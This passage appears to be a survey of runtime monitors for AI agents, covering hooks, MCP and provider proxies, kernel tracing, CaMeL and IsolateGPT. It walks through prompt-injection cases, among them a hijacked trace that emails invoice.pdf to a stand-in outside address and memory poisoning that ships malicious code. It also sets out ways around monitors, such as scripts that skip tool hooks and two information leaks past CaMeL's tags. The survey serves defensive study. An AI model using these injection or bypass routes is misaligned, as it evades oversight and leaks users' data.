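# Monitoring and mediating the tool calls and internal messages of AI agents at runtime

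## What it means to mediate an agent's actions at runtime

An AI agent is a software system in which a language model chooses actions and ordinary code carries them out. A chatbot's mistake stays on the screen until a person acts on it, but an agent can send an email or delete a file itself. Runtime monitoring places a second program, the monitor, between the model's choice and its effect, where it checks the action while it can still be stopped. Unlike better training and pre-release testing, which try to improve the model, a runtime monitor leaves the model and its faults unchanged and checks what the agent does.

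### The agent loop

The model at the centre of an agent runs nothing itself. As Anthropic's *How tool use works* explains to developers, the model only emits a structured request, and other code executes it. That request is a tool call. The sample call in Anthropic's *Handle tool calls* consists of a tool name (`get_weather`), an identifier, and an input that gives San Francisco as the location and Celsius as the unit. Because the call has named fields, a program can check it without having to interpret prose. The loop around it runs as follows:

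1. The application sends the model its context: the developer's instructions, the list of available tools, the user's request and everything that has happened so far.
2. The model replies with a final answer or with one or more tool calls.
3. The application runs each tool call.
4. The application appends the results to the context and sends the whole back to the model.
5. The cycle repeats until the model replies without asking for a tool.

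In *Unrolling the Codex agent loop*, an account of OpenAI's coding agent, Bolin (2026) warns that an agent might make hundreds of tool calls for a single request before it hands control back to the user.

Between steps 2 and 3, the action has been proposed but not carried out, and a monitor meant to prevent harm has to act then. The application has no such chance with some tools. For example, Anthropic runs web search and a few other tools on its own servers, and the application usually learns of the call after it has finished. Step 4 matters because whatever a tool returns becomes part of the text from which the model picks its next action, and some of that text comes from strangers.

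Many agents have components beyond a model and a loop, such as a planner that breaks the task into steps, a memory store that keeps notes between sessions, or a subagent that takes over part of the work. Each component has its own inputs and outputs, and whatever one passes to another is a message. Zhou and Zhang (2026), in *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents*, describe an assistant that drafts a report from approved records, hands the draft to another agent for review and then sends the result outside the organisation. A monitor can intercept the message to the reviewing agent just as it can intercept a tool call. The design in *DelegateGuard* (2026) routes tool calls, memory writes, messages between agents and requests to delegate work through one monitor.

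Internal messages are worth monitoring because damage spreads through them. Hossain, Hossain and Ansari (2026) reviewed 85 papers in *On Understanding, Identifying, and Mitigating Vulnerabilities in Agentic Large Language Models* and concluded that weak isolation lets a fault in one layer of an agent spread to the others, sometimes with no visible effect until after many intermediate actions. A monitor that checks only outgoing tool calls could detect such a fault only at its last stage.

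### Why an agent needs watching

An agent reads the user's instructions in the same context as everything else, and the model cannot reliably tell instructions from data. In *Kairos*, Hempel, Loose and colleagues (2026) trace prompt injection to this weakness. Anyone who controls a web page, a file or an incoming message that the agent will read can plant an instruction in it, and the agent may then carry it out with the user's permissions. Among the attacks they list, text in a code repository led a coding assistant to leak private SSH keys (credentials for logging in to other machines), and calendar invitations made assistants act against their users. Several of the attacks needed no software bug.

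An email assistant might have three tools. `read_inbox` fetches messages, `search_contacts` looks someone up in the address book, and `send_email` sends a message with or without an attachment. The user asks for a summary of each day's mail. One day, a message from a sender the user does not know contains a line telling the assistant to forward the latest invoice to an outside address. Here is the trace, the ordered record of calls and results, for an ordinary day and for the day of the attack.

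| Step | Normal trace | Hijacked trace |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | `read_inbox(day: today)` returns the day's messages | `read_inbox(day: today)` returns the day's messages, one with the planted instruction |
| 2 | `search_contacts(name: "Okafor")` returns a colleague's entry | `search_contacts(name: "Okafor")` returns a colleague's entry |
| 3 | The user receives the summary | `send_email(to: "ap@northfold.example", attachment: "invoice.pdf")` returns "sent" |
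| 4 | | The user receives the summary |

The traces differ by one call. The call is well formed, it uses a tool that the developer supplied on purpose, and the user's account is allowed to send mail. The user might ask for the same call on another day. The summary may not reveal the difference either, since the model can write the same one after both traces. The call is wrong only because of its context. The user wanted a summary, and the address came from a stranger's email. *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (2026) makes the same point about longer attacks, in which a planted instruction steers the agent through a harmful sequence of individually ordinary calls.

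The assistant can make mistakes without being attacked. If the address book holds two people named Okafor, the model may write to the wrong one. It may also answer a meeting invitation that the user only wanted to hear about. Hossain and colleagues count faulty calls and unintended code execution among the agent failures that can do irreversible harm. *Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026) names two causes of harmful actions: prompt injection and misalignment, in which the model itself pursues something other than what its user wants.

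A monitor that checks actions receives the same `send_email` call whatever caused it, so it can stop the email without diagnosing the model. Deciding whether the email should be stopped is harder. The address's provenance, or the record of where it came from, reveals the planted instruction but not the mix-up between two Okafors, because both of their addresses come from the user's own contacts.

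Research has so far concentrated on agents' inputs. In the sample that Hossain and colleagues reviewed, which ends in December 2025, 66% of the papers dealt with weaknesses in what the agent takes in, such as prompt injection, and 4.7% (four papers) dealt with weaknesses at the point of action. The newer systems in this section suggest that research has since begun to shift toward the point of action.

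### The reference monitor

The idea of a checkpoint that every action must pass is much older than AI agents. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) reports a panel's work on how people with different security clearances could share one US Air Force computer. The panel was worried about a malicious user with legitimate access who could write and run his own programs. It proposed the reference monitor, a mechanism that checks every reference a program makes to data, a device or another program against a list of what that program may do on its user's behalf. The panel required that nobody be able to tamper with the mechanism, that the system always invoke it, and that it be small enough for analysis and tests to cover completely.

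Anderson used the HIS 635, a commercial machine of the day, and its operating system, GCOS III, to illustrate failure. The hardware confined each user's program to its own region of memory. But the program needed the operating system for input and output, and most of the operating system ran with that confinement switched off, so the check did not always apply. Even if the operating system is counted as the monitor, it was too large, at 200,000 to 300,000 instructions, and a number of successful penetration exercises had already shown that it could be tampered with.

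Security engineers call the "always invoked" requirement complete mediation. In Saltzer and Schroeder's classic list of design principles, it means that the system checks every access to every object. *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (Tallam, 2026) extends their term to cover every step of the agent's loop, starting when the agent forms a plan.

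Complete mediation is hard to secure for agents. Zhou and Zhang observe that one agent action can affect several tools, other agents and outside services. Hempel and colleagues add that a monitor at the tool layer observes only what the agent declares as a tool call. If the email assistant has a tool for running code, a short script can mail the invoice without a `send_email` call appearing in the trace. Complete mediation by such a monitor therefore rests on an assumption about how the system is set up. Codex's sandbox is an example of a partial boundary. It covers the shell tool that comes with Codex, but according to Bolin, tools from servers that follow the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a widely used standard for connecting agents to tools, must supply their own guardrails.

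Claims to have built a reference monitor for agents should therefore be read together with their conditions. *Causality Laundering* (2026) claims all three of Anderson's properties for a proxy that sits between the model and an MCP tool server, runs as a separate process and applies four layers of deterministic checks. Its claim of complete mediation holds when the deployment has no other path to the tools. *Scan the Skill, Govern the Action* (2026) claims less for its own monitor, describing it as only partly tamper-proof and dependent on a pattern matcher that an adversary can bypass.

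Even a flawless reference monitor of Anderson's kind would pass the hijacked call, because its list records what a user may do and this user may send mail. Hempel and colleagues call an agent in this position a confused deputy, an old term from computer security, because it stays within its authority but uses that authority for somebody else. The reference monitor therefore specifies where to place a check and how robust to make it, but not what it should check for.

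### Mediation and enforcement

Mediation means that every call or message goes through the monitor before it takes effect, and enforcement means that the system acts on the monitor's judgement. An organisation can have either without much of the other. If the monitor only logs each call, the log will help someone reconstruct how an invoice was sent, but it won't stop the invoice from being sent. If the monitor can block `send_email` but the agent can also reach the mail server from a script, the agent can still send email without going through the monitor.

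Hempel and colleagues build their system around a closely related split between what they call confinement and authorization. Confinement ensures that no effect leaves the agent's environment before the monitor releases it. They claim this holds even for a fully hostile agent, provided that the isolation layer and the monitor are sound. Authorization is the decision about which effects to release. They promise much less for it, because it depends on tracing where data came from and guessing what the user wanted. Tallam instead separates a single decision about the agent's intent from the network, identity, device and data controls that enforce that decision.

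Besides allowing or refusing an action, a monitor can hold an email until a person has looked at it, strip the attachment, or undo a change to a file. A monitor that must allow or refuse each action immediately can base its decision only on the trace so far, which limits the policies it can enforce.

### Written rules and learned profiles

A monitor must judge an action after mediating it and before enforcing a decision, and it can do so in two ways. One is to apply a rule that somebody wrote. Sistla and colleagues demonstrate this with a coding agent that may read a company's inventory file but must not send it out. The agent uploads a harmless status report, copies the inventory over the report, and then uploads the report again. Their rule permits uploads only of files labelled "public". The monitor allows the first upload, relabels the report "sensitive" when the inventory is copied over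 it, and refuses the second upload, even though the command is identical.

The rule is a few lines long, but it depends on a lot of earlier work. Someone had to label the inventory as sensitive, and the monitor had to encode what copying and uploading do to data. Zhou and Zhang also point out that whoever turns a requirement into a rule can lose part of its meaning. For the email assistant, the rule "send only to addresses that the user has typed" would stop the theft of the invoice, but it would also stop the assistant when the user says "reply to everyone who asked for the slides".

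Hempel and colleagues tested two versions of their system on AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office tasks with planted prompt injections. The full version, which passes doubtful cases to a language model or a person, completed 85.1% of the tasks when not under attack. A strict version, which refused every action its written policy did not clearly allow, completed only 42.7% and stopped no more attacks, within the variation between runs. A language model judge needs little preparation, but it reads the same untrusted content as the agent, so an attacker can try to inject instructions into it too.

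The other way is to learn a profile, a description of normal behaviour drawn from past traces, and to flag whatever deviates from it. Intrusion detection did this with the system calls of ordinary programs long before there were agents. Suppose that in a few hundred earlier sessions, requests for a summary led to `read_inbox`, often to `search_contacts`, and never to `send_email`. The hijacked trace would then stand out even if no one had anticipated an attack involving invoices. A profile has different prerequisites from a rule. It requires enough traces of the same kind of work, reasonable confidence that none of them contains an attack, a threshold for how much deviation to tolerate, and an agent whose behaviour stays roughly the same over time.

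Most of the defences that ship with tool-using agents are so far rule-based, according to *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents*. *Scan the Skill, Govern the Action* reports that commercial platforms already intervene on anomalous behaviour and that some of their customers run thousands of agents. This adoption is evidence of demand, but it does not show how accurate the platforms are.

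The value of a learned monitor depends on what it can observe, what counts as normal, and what a deviation proves. A monitor that watches only named tools will miss an invoice sent through a script, however good its profile is. Normal behavior is hard to define because the same request can send the model down a different path each time. A deviation doesn't prove an attack, because the first time the user really does ask the assistant to forward an invoice, the `send_email` call will look as strange as it did when the invoice was stolen. The monitor may also miss a planted instruction that makes the assistant leave one awkward message out of the summary, since the sequence of calls may be normal.

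## Where tool calls can be intercepted

A tool call, such as one that sends an email, passes through several layers of software before it takes effect, and a monitor can sit in any of them. *Agent Behavioral Contracts II* (Bhardwaj, Singh and Bhardwaj, 2026) describes three interception points, which it calls planes: a hook inside the agent framework, a proxy on the tool protocol, and a proxy on the connection to the model provider. Other systems catch the effects of a call further down, in the operating system's kernel or on the network, which adds a fourth interception point, although the paper holds that there are only three. The paper's account of the planes is an engineering analysis. Its experiments measure how often agents that share a model fail together and do not compare the planes.

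As described above, the email assistant can leak the invoice to a stranger by calling `send_email` or, if it also has a tool for running code (call it `run_script`), by running a script. The stranger receives the same file either way, but what a monitor observes can differ greatly between the two, depending on where the monitor is placed.

### A hook inside the agent framework

An agent framework is the library that runs the agent loop. Many frameworks let developers register a function, called a hook, that runs just before each tool call. The hook receives the parsed call, the identity of the agent that made it, and any other session data the framework keeps. For `send_email`, this is nearly everything a monitor could use. The hook can compare the recipient's address with the user's request for a summary and block the call before the tool runs.

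A hook written for one framework may not work in another, because each has its own convention for refusing a call. One requires the hook to return false and another requires it to raise an error. Bhardwaj and colleagues keep the policy in one place and write a thin adapter for each convention. In an early version of their library, however, one adapter delivered the session's state in a nested form and another in a flat form. As a result, a rule that worked during enforcement silently evaluated to false during measurement, and the same rule produced two different compliance rates.

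Some frameworks don't let a hook block a tool call before it runs. If the hook runs only after the tool has finished, it can keep the result from the model, but the tool has already acted, for example by sending an invoice. Bhardwaj and colleagues call this post-action denial and treat it as a form of redaction. Their library includes a table of which frameworks allow blocking beforehand, because a setting labelled "enforcement enabled" could otherwise mean only that results are withheld afterwards.

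*AEGIS* (Yuan, Su and Zhao, 2026) avoids most of the adapter work by patching the client libraries that agents use to call model providers. The developer adds two lines of code to install the patch. When a model's reply contains a tool call, the patch suspends the agent, sends the tool's name and arguments to a separate gateway program and waits for a decision. The gateway extracts every text string from the arguments, checks them against 22 attack patterns, applies the developer's policies, and then allows the call, blocks it or holds it for a person to review. The system supports 14 frameworks in Python, JavaScript and Go.

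In their tests, it blocked all 48 attacks in a suite they assembled, wrongly flagged 6 of 500 benign calls (1.2%), and added a median of 8.3 milliseconds per call. The six false alarms were all database queries containing a legitimate "or", which resembles a common attack. The attacks come from much the same categories as the detector's patterns, so the perfect score is better evidence that the interception works than that the detector would recognise new attacks.

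The script is harder for any hook to check. The hook receives a `run_script` call, whose argument is the code or perhaps only the name of a file that the agent saved earlier. Once the script is running, its traffic does not pass through the hook. Yuan and colleagues exclude such calls from what AEGIS defends against. *Governed MCP* (Son, 2026) makes the more basic objection that a safety library inside the agent's process has the same privileges as the agent, so code running there can skip the check, replace it or change its verdict without exploiting any bug. This objection applies only if the agent can get code to run in that process, which a model limited to the assistant's three email tools could not do.

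### A proxy on the tool protocol

Agents that use MCP send tool calls as structured messages to a tool server, which may run on the same machine or belong to another company. A proxy between the agent and the server receives the tool's name, its arguments and, afterwards, the result. For `send_email`, it sees the same recipient and attachment as the hook, and it can block the call. One proxy works with every framework that uses MCP, and Bhardwaj and colleagues consider this the only interception point that is both structured and independent of the framework. With the gateway design in *Securing the Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2025), users notice no change, but the gateway adds latency, gives the organisation more infrastructure to run and creates a single point of failure.

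A proxy can also act before the model chooses a tool. Agents first request a list of tools from the server, and the proxy in *Prompts Don't Protect* (2026) returns only those that the agent's role permits. An assistant with a read-only role would not see `send_email` in the list. *Containing the Autonomous Operator* (2026) describes a design for agents on the Kubernetes container platform in which the gateway stores a fingerprint of each tool's description when someone approves it, so that later changes can be detected. The gateway can also label tool results with where they came from.

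The proxy does not receive the model's reasoning, or the user's request unless someone arranges to pass it along. It also covers only MCP traffic. If `run_script` is built into the agent, as Codex's shell tool is, the script can steal the invoice without producing an MCP message. If `run_script` is an MCP tool, the proxy receives one message containing code, but the email the script then sends does not pass through the proxy.

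*Containing the Autonomous Operator* closes that route with a network rule that restricts the agent's containers to the gateway and a short list of permitted destinations. The script still runs, but it cannot connect to an outside mail server. *From Tool Connection to Execution Control* (2026) sets out eight security properties for agent runtimes, specifies the entry points at which each holds, and gives counterexamples for traffic that arrives any other way. It also explains that a well-formed MCP message does not prove that the caller has authority to run it. The check has to cover the operation that would actually execute and the file or account that a name in the message refers to.

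### A proxy on the connection to the model provider

A third kind of proxy sits between the agent and the model, relaying the context the agent sends and the tool calls the model returns. It needs no support from the framework, and often the only change on the agent's side is the address it sends requests to.

The traffic through the proxy includes the user's request for a summary, the stranger's email with the planted line and the `send_email` call. But the proxy has to reconstruct these from each provider's wire format. Bhardwaj and colleagues add that when several agents share a process, the proxy needs further information to identify which one made a call. The proxy can block a call by withholding the reply that contains it, since an application cannot run a call it never received. This does not work for tools that the provider runs itself, such as web search.

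The proxy receives somewhat less information about the script than about the email call. If the model wrote the script during this session, the script's text went through the proxy, and a monitor could try to work out what it does. But the proxy receives no information about the run itself, such as which files the script opened or where it connected, unless the script prints it and the output goes back to the model.

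Any of these proxies can crash or lose contact with its policy store. The system fails closed if it then denies every call, and fails open if it lets them through. Bhardwaj and colleagues argue for recording unchecked calls as a third outcome, "unevaluated", because counting them as compliant makes the agent look more reliable than it is, and counting them as violations makes it look less reliable.

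### The kernel and the network

A program opens a file, starts another program or connects to a remote machine by making a system call, which is a request to the kernel at the core of the operating system. The script must make system calls too, so the two thefts look alike at this level. In each, a process opens `invoice.pdf`, reads it and connects to a remote address.

A legitimate email looks the same at the system-call level. System calls include the file's path and the remote machine's IP address, but the recipient's email address is usually encrypted, and the user's request does not appear at all. If the email tool runs on another company's server, the local kernel handles only the connection to that server, not the sending of the email.

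A monitor can recover the meaning of events by recording the agent's conversation with the model alongside them. *AgentSight* (2025) does this with eBPF, a mechanism for loading small verified programs into a running kernel. It captures the decrypted traffic between agent and model to find what the agent was trying to do, and it records system calls to find the effects. *AgentLoupe* (Bao, Liu and colleagues, 2026) reports that AgentSight loses the link between the two when an action happens later or in a process that does not descend from the one that started it. Its own tool attaches a label for each model exchange to the kernel's records of processes, files and network connections, with an average overhead below 8%. An investigator can then trace a file written one day and executed the next back to the exchange that produced it. Both tools record actions but do not block them.

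| Interception point | The `send_email` call | The script | Can it block? | What it takes to install |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Framework hook | Tool, arguments, agent and session state | A `run_script` call, perhaps with the code | Yes, where the framework allows refusal in advance | An adapter per framework, or patched client libraries |
| MCP proxy | Tool, arguments and result | One `run_script` message, or nothing if the tool is built in | Yes, before the tool runs | Routing tool traffic through it and closing other routes |
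| Provider proxy | The call and the conversation around it | The code, if the model wrote it in this session | Yes, except for tools the provider runs | Routing model traffic through it, and a parser for each provider's format |
| Kernel or network | A file read and a connection | A file read and a connection | Yes, if built for it | Privileged access to the machine, and decryption to read contents |

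### Checking that no path avoids the monitor

Complete mediation is easy to claim for any of these designs but tedious to verify. Son's *Governed MCP* is unusual in counting the paths from agent to system and how many of them are mediated. Son wrote an experimental operating system, Anima OS, in which agents run inside a sandbox and a gateway in the kernel judges their tool calls. The paper's first version claimed "123 paths, 100% mediated". The revised version withdraws that claim and reports a new count, in which the gateway mediates 43 of 59 paths.

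The 59 paths consist of 18 functions that the sandbox offers to agents, 20 registered MCP tools, and 21 system calls open to ordinary programs. The gateway checks 15 of the sandbox functions, all 20 tools and 8 of the system calls. Ten of the remaining 16 paths need no check, because five only read catalogues or other metadata and five touch no resource that the policy governs. The gateway therefore checks 43 of the 49 paths that need it. The other six are system calls that reach governed resources. Some of them store and fetch data, and some send and receive messages, which could let agents communicate outside any monitor's view. Son has deferred checks on these six to a later release.

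Part of the evidence is that the sandbox cannot reach the inner function that executes a tool call. For the 20 tools, a test program also sent trial calls through the gateway without executing them and confirmed that each received a verdict. The count covers only direct calls through the documented interface, on a single system start, and depends on the correctness of the compiler that confines the agent's code. It was also feasible because Son controls the whole operating system. Such a list would be harder to draw up on ordinary Linux, which has hundreds of system calls and can have any number of installed programs.

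The gateway runs in the kernel, which protects it from the agent, but it receives structured calls through the tool protocol and so does not have to infer their meaning from file reads. The fixed checks and the audit record take 11.3 microseconds per call. A safety verdict from a small language model takes about 358 milliseconds, which limits the system to roughly 2.8 calls per second. On 101 test calls that Son labelled himself, the gateway stopped 30 of 37 dangerous calls and 9 of 64 benign ones. Without the language model, it stopped only 10 of the dangerous calls.

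### Inferring actions from operating-system events

Tether and ActPlane both try to get back from system calls to something a policy can use. Tether, the system behind the inventory example in the previous section, does so by running each command before deciding whether to allow it:

1. The command runs in a disposable layer on top of the file system, so that its changes land in a scratch directory and not in the real files.
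2. A tracing program records every system call, and a local proxy holds each outgoing network request.
3. Tether translates the record into a few of eleven abstract actions. If a process reads one file and then writes another, Tether infers a copy. If a process reads a file and then contacts a remote machine, it infers an upload.
4. The monitor checks the actions against the policy. If it approves them, Tether commits the changes and forwards the requests, and otherwise it discards both.

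Kairos also holds effects until a monitor releases them, but Tether's particular contribution is the translation. The invoice script becomes "upload `invoice.pdf` to this host", whatever language it is written in and however many temporary files it uses. The translation deliberately overestimates what was copied. If a script reads one file and writes unrelated data to another, Tether treats the first file as copied to the second, because system calls do not show which bytes went where.

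Sistla and colleagues tested Tether on recorded sessions from two benchmarks for coding agents, MonitoringBenchHonest (system administration) and LinuxArena (software engineering). The agent does its main task in the benign sessions and also pursues a harmful side task in the adversarial ones. They rebuilt each environment, replayed the commands one at a time and applied the same rules throughout, changing only the file labels and permitted hosts between tasks. For comparison, they tested Auto Mode, the language-model judge in Anthropic's coding agent Claude Code, on the same sessions, once with its default rules and once with Tether's policy written into its instructions. Recall here is the share of adversarial sessions that the monitor blocked.

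| Monitor | MonitoringBenchHonest: recall | False-positive rate | LinuxArena: recall | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Tether | 100% (199 of 199) | 2.3% | 100% (145 of 145) | 5.0% |
| Auto Mode, default | 86.9% | 35.3% | 97.9% | 5.7% |
| Auto Mode with Tether's policy | 82.4% | 14.7% | 98.6% | 1.7% |

Sistla and colleagues measured the 100% only on sessions in which every action ran in the foreground, left a complete trace and had a meaning that Tether models. Outside that set, they estimate that 28.2% of MonitoringBenchHonest sessions and 22.1% of LinuxArena sessions require somebody to read the content, for instance because the agent makes a malicious edit to a file it is allowed to edit. Another 36.3% and 71.5%, respectively, involve background processes or databases. A stricter policy can detect that an agent is using one of these channels and block it or ask the user, but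 Tether cannot yet follow data through them. The comparison with Auto Mode also favours Tether because the sessions were chosen to suit it, although Auto Mode did miss attacks hidden inside scripts, as one would expect from a judge that reads only the command line.

The false-positive rates also call for some caution, because Sistla and colleagues refined the policy by repeatedly running it on benchmark traces and adjusting rules that blocked too much. An organisation writing its own policy for unfamiliar work would probably see more false alarms at first. Of the 74 benign sessions that Tether flagged, 50 involved unrequested edits to protected files and 7 involved undeclared hosts. One could defend those refusals. The other 17 came from broad searches that opened secret files in passing, and a monitor that works from system calls cannot detect that the agent ignored their contents.

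A second model also attacked Tether in a small mock environment, trying to steal a file in five tasks and to alter a protected one in five others. The attacker succeeded 40% of the time against an early version and never against the third, after fixes to gaps in the tracing. Each of Tether's failures had a specific cause that a programmer could fix. The prototype is slow because its tracing program adds a lot of overhead, and it decrypts web traffic only for the emulated services in the tests.

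*ActPlane* (Zheng, Wu and colleagues, 2026) enforces rules on the live system rather than in a rehearsal. It argues that enforcement belongs in the operating system, the only place where it can cover every route to an effect, whereas *Containing the Autonomous Operator* calls the tool boundary the most important point of control. ActPlane's eBPF programs attach labels to processes, files and network endpoints, and the labels spread as data moves. A process that reads a labelled invoice acquires the label, and a rule can then block it from connecting to the outside. Depending on the rule, ActPlane denies the system call beforehand, kills the process just after it, or only notifies the agent. The labels also carry history, which allows rules such as "no commit until the tests have passed since the last edit".

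ActPlane's evaluation tested whether the system catches indirect violations, using 38 rules from the instruction files of 15 software projects. A coding agent generated five traces for each rule, 190 in all. Of each five, two obey the rule, one breaks it directly through a tool call, one breaks it through a script written earlier, and one breaks it through a harmless-looking file that triggers the forbidden action. A trace ended correctly if the agent returned to compliance after a violation or finished a permitted task without wrongful interference. With ActPlane, 75.8% of traces ended correctly. A language-model filter, pattern matching on tool calls and a data-flow tracker at the tool level scored between 45.3% and 48.9%, and all three caught almost none of the violations triggered by harmless-looking files.

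That score combines detection with the agent's response. A version of ActPlane that returned only a bare refusal detected 75.4% of violations, nearly as many as the full system's 77.2%, but scored 53.7% because the agent seldom worked out what to do instead. The tool-level monitors detected 34% to 40%. ActPlane's misses came mostly from rules that a language model had translated too narrowly, while rules translated too broadly caused 17 of its 18 false alarms on 76 compliant traces. Detection rose to 94.7% after one round of corrections, but Zheng and colleagues measured this on the traces that had prompted the corrections.

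ActPlane added 1.9% overhead on replayed agent sessions and at most 8.4% on a heavy software build. In a separate test on 361 workplace tasks, the unprotected agent behaved unsafely in 106, and ActPlane stopped 78 of those. It also intervened in 16% of the tasks that had been safe without it. The 28 it missed included harmful chat messages, harmful text inside files, and changes made within a remote service, which the kernel's hooks cannot observe. An email sent through a company's mail service can be one of these remote changes, in which case a monitor has to get the recipient and the attachment from the tool call.

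## How an agent is divided into components with monitored boundaries

Every agent has a boundary at the tool call. Any other boundaries depend on the agent's design. One email assistant might have a planner, a memory store and a tool executor that exchange structured messages, which a monitor can watch. Another might do the same work with one model and a long prompt, so it has no internal messages to monitor.

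Designers can divide an agent by function, with a component for each job. They can divide it by trust, separating the components that read untrusted text from those that can act. Or they can divide it by resource, with a kernel that controls access to memory, tools and outside input. Each method requires different initial information and leaves different gaps.

### Testing whether a boundary is real

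A monitored boundary works only if all data that crosses it travels in messages the monitor receives. A designer can test this by listing everything that both components can read or write and checking whether data could pass between them another way.

Shared context often lets one component influence another without sending it a message. *IsolateGPT* (Wu, Roesner and colleagues, 2024) describes assistants that load the descriptions of all installed apps into one model's context. A ride-hailing app could plant an instruction there to inflate a rival's fare whenever the user compares prices. A monitor on messages between apps would miss this because the two apps never exchange any.

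Shared memory can do the same thing more slowly. *AgentKernel* (Zou, Guo and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a software team whose agents review and deploy code. A comment on a proposed change contains a planted instruction, and the reviewing agent's summary of the comment goes into long-term memory. A deploying agent later retrieves the summary as trusted context and ships malicious code. The memory store can pass the test only if the monitor also covers every read and write, and the monitor needs a record of where each entry came from to do much with those reads and writes.

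### Dividing by function

Developers start with a list of the agent's jobs. AWS's *AGENTREL01-BP02 Establish modular, fault-isolated layers*, guidance for developers who build agents on Amazon's cloud, recommends separate layers for compute, memory, reasoning, orchestration and tool integration. The developers publish a contract for the messages at each boundary and give each layer its own execution resources. They also set an error rate at which the caller stops calling a layer and uses something simpler, such as the current session's context in place of long-term memory.

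The purpose is reliability, so that a broken memory store doesn't take the whole agent down, but a security monitor benefits too. It can reject a message that breaks the contract, and messages of one known type are easier to profile than a mixture. (Where nobody designed such layers, a monitor can try to recover units of execution from past traces, as the next section explains.)

Dividing an agent by function does not separate what is trusted from what is not. The planner has to read tool results, including the stranger's email, and choose the next call. Every message satisfies its contract, because the planted instruction arrives as text in a field meant for text and the stolen data leaves in a valid `send_email` request.

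### Dividing by trust: the two-model design

To divide an agent by trust, the designer has to identify which inputs an outsider could have written and which components can cause an effect, then make sure that no component both reads those inputs and can cause an effect. Willison's dual-LLM pattern of 2023 applies this to language models. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) explains that a privileged model plans and issues tool calls but never reads untrusted data directly, while a quarantined model reads untrusted data but can only return values.

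CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues introduced in 2025, puts ordinary code between the two models. According to *CaMeLoT* (2026), a later system that builds on it, CaMeL works as follows:

1. The privileged model receives the user's request and writes a plan in a restricted form of Python.
2. An interpreter runs the plan and makes the tool calls itself.
3. Where the plan needs something from untrusted text, the quarantined model extracts it.
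4. The interpreter stores the extracted value in a variable, with a tag that records its sources and who may read it.
5. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs policy functions that check those tags.

For the email assistant, the plan might look like this:

```
mail    = read_inbox(day="today")
name    = ask_quarantined("Which colleague needs a reply?", mail)
contact = search_contacts(name=name)
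summary = ask_quarantined("Summarise these messages.", mail)
show_user(summary, contact)
```

The planted instruction reaches the quarantined model twice. It can distort the summary or produce the wrong name, but the plan has no `send_email` line and the quarantined model cannot add one.

The damage a corrupted answer can do depends on what the quarantined model may return. *SPA* (2026) gives that model no tools and no memory of the plan, and restricts each reply to a fixed schema for that step. A reply that must be a date leaves little room for an attack, far less than a free-text summary does.

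The tags matter when the plan does send something. Suppose the user asks the assistant to send the invoice to the address in Okafor's latest message, and an attacker has inserted a different address into that message. The assistant would follow the correct plan but send the invoice to the wrong recipient. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) distinguishes control flow (which actions the agent takes) from data flow (which values it uses), and notes that the two-model split does not by itself guarantee safe data flow. CaMeL's policies are meant to fill this gap. A policy could block the agent from sending a confidential file to anyone outside the file's list of permitted readers, even if the quarantined model took the address from a poisoned message.

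Such policies reduce an agent's utility. Garby and colleagues report that CaMeL's utility on the banking tasks in AgentDojo halves when its policy checks are on. Some tasks also don't fit the design. If the user says "do whatever the checklist in this email says", the necessary steps exist only in untrusted text, which the planner never reads, so it cannot plan them.

### Isolating whole apps

Wu and colleagues draw the trust boundary around each app. In their system, IsolateGPT, each third-party app runs in a separate process, called a spoke, with its own language model and memory. A central hub receives the user's requests and relays messages between spokes. The code that handles messages at either end, called an operator, contains no language model, so it cannot follow a planted instruction.

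If the email app needs a file from a cloud-drive app, its operator requests that capability from the hub without knowing which app provides it. The hub returns the required formats for the request and the response. The operator then sends its request through the hub to the drive app, and the answer comes back the same way. The user approves the initial enquiry, the request and the answer, and the hub warns the user if the collaboration was not in its plan for the task. Operators may be able to validate dates, integers and web addresses without the user. A person still needs to check free text, because Wu and colleagues knew of no foolproof detector for malicious instructions.

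On a set of standard tasks, IsolateGPT matched the functionality of a version without isolation, and its overhead stayed under 30% for about three-quarters of the queries. But Wu and colleagues exclude attacks that stay within one app. The theft of the invoice is such an attack if the email app already holds the file and provides `read_inbox`, `search_contacts` and `send_email`. The stranger's message takes over the email spoke, and no message crosses to another spoke. IsolateGPT asks the user before an app sends an email, so stopping the theft would depend on the user reading the prompt carefully. If the invoice were in the cloud drive, the hub could also inspect the request for the file.

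### Proofs about an agent and its monitor

CaMeL came without a formal proof, and its designers called formalising it crucial further work. Garby and colleagues have since described two ways around its tags. CaMeL normally blocks code that checks whether an account balance exceeds a threshold and sends an email if it does, because whether the email is sent would reveal secret information about the balance. In one bypass, the code first sets a variable, `rich`, to true and then uses an intermediate variable to set `rich` to false only if the balance is low. When the balance is high, the line that changes `rich` never runs, so CaMeL doesn't tag `rich` as secret, and the code can send the email if `rich` is true.

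The other leak goes through a retry loop outside the tag-tracking interpreter. Whether CaMeL's policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt can reveal one bit. The loop lets an adaptive program retry until it has the whole secret. In both cases, information crosses the boundary without a tagged value.

In response, Garby and colleagues designed a small programming language for agents. Every value and every conversation with a model has a label, such as "untrusted" or "secret". A conversation's label combines the labels of all messages sent to the model, so one untrusted email makes the whole conversation untrusted. A program can fork a conversation, let the model read the email in the copy and then discard the copy. This lets the programmer create the two-model separation wherever a task needs it.

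Their main theorem is a form of noninterference. Roughly, if an observer has no access to the secret inputs, changing those inputs does not change the probabilities of what the observer receives. The theorem covers every program in the language, including agents that write and run their own code, but not information that leaks through whether a program finishes. The Lean proof assistant checked the proof, which applies to the same interpreter that calls the model. In tests on AgentDojo's banking tasks, an agent written in the language completed about as many tasks as CaMeL with its policy checks turned off, and resisted the attacks in all but two of 1,296 attacked runs. The guarantee depends on the initial labels. If a tool marks a stranger's email as trusted, the interpreter will propagate the wrong label.

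Noninterference is too strict for many useful agents, such as an assistant that deliberately discloses private data when it answers meeting requests with the user's availability. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) therefore compares the agent with a reference agent that runs the same plan under the same monitor, but whose model never obeys untrusted text. The real agent is relatively secure if, whenever an attacker can tell two secrets apart by attacking it, some input to the reference agent would also let the attacker tell them apart.

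The monitor in this framework has a state, a function that allows or denies each request, and a function that updates the state after other events. In the simplest version the state is a set *C* of tools:

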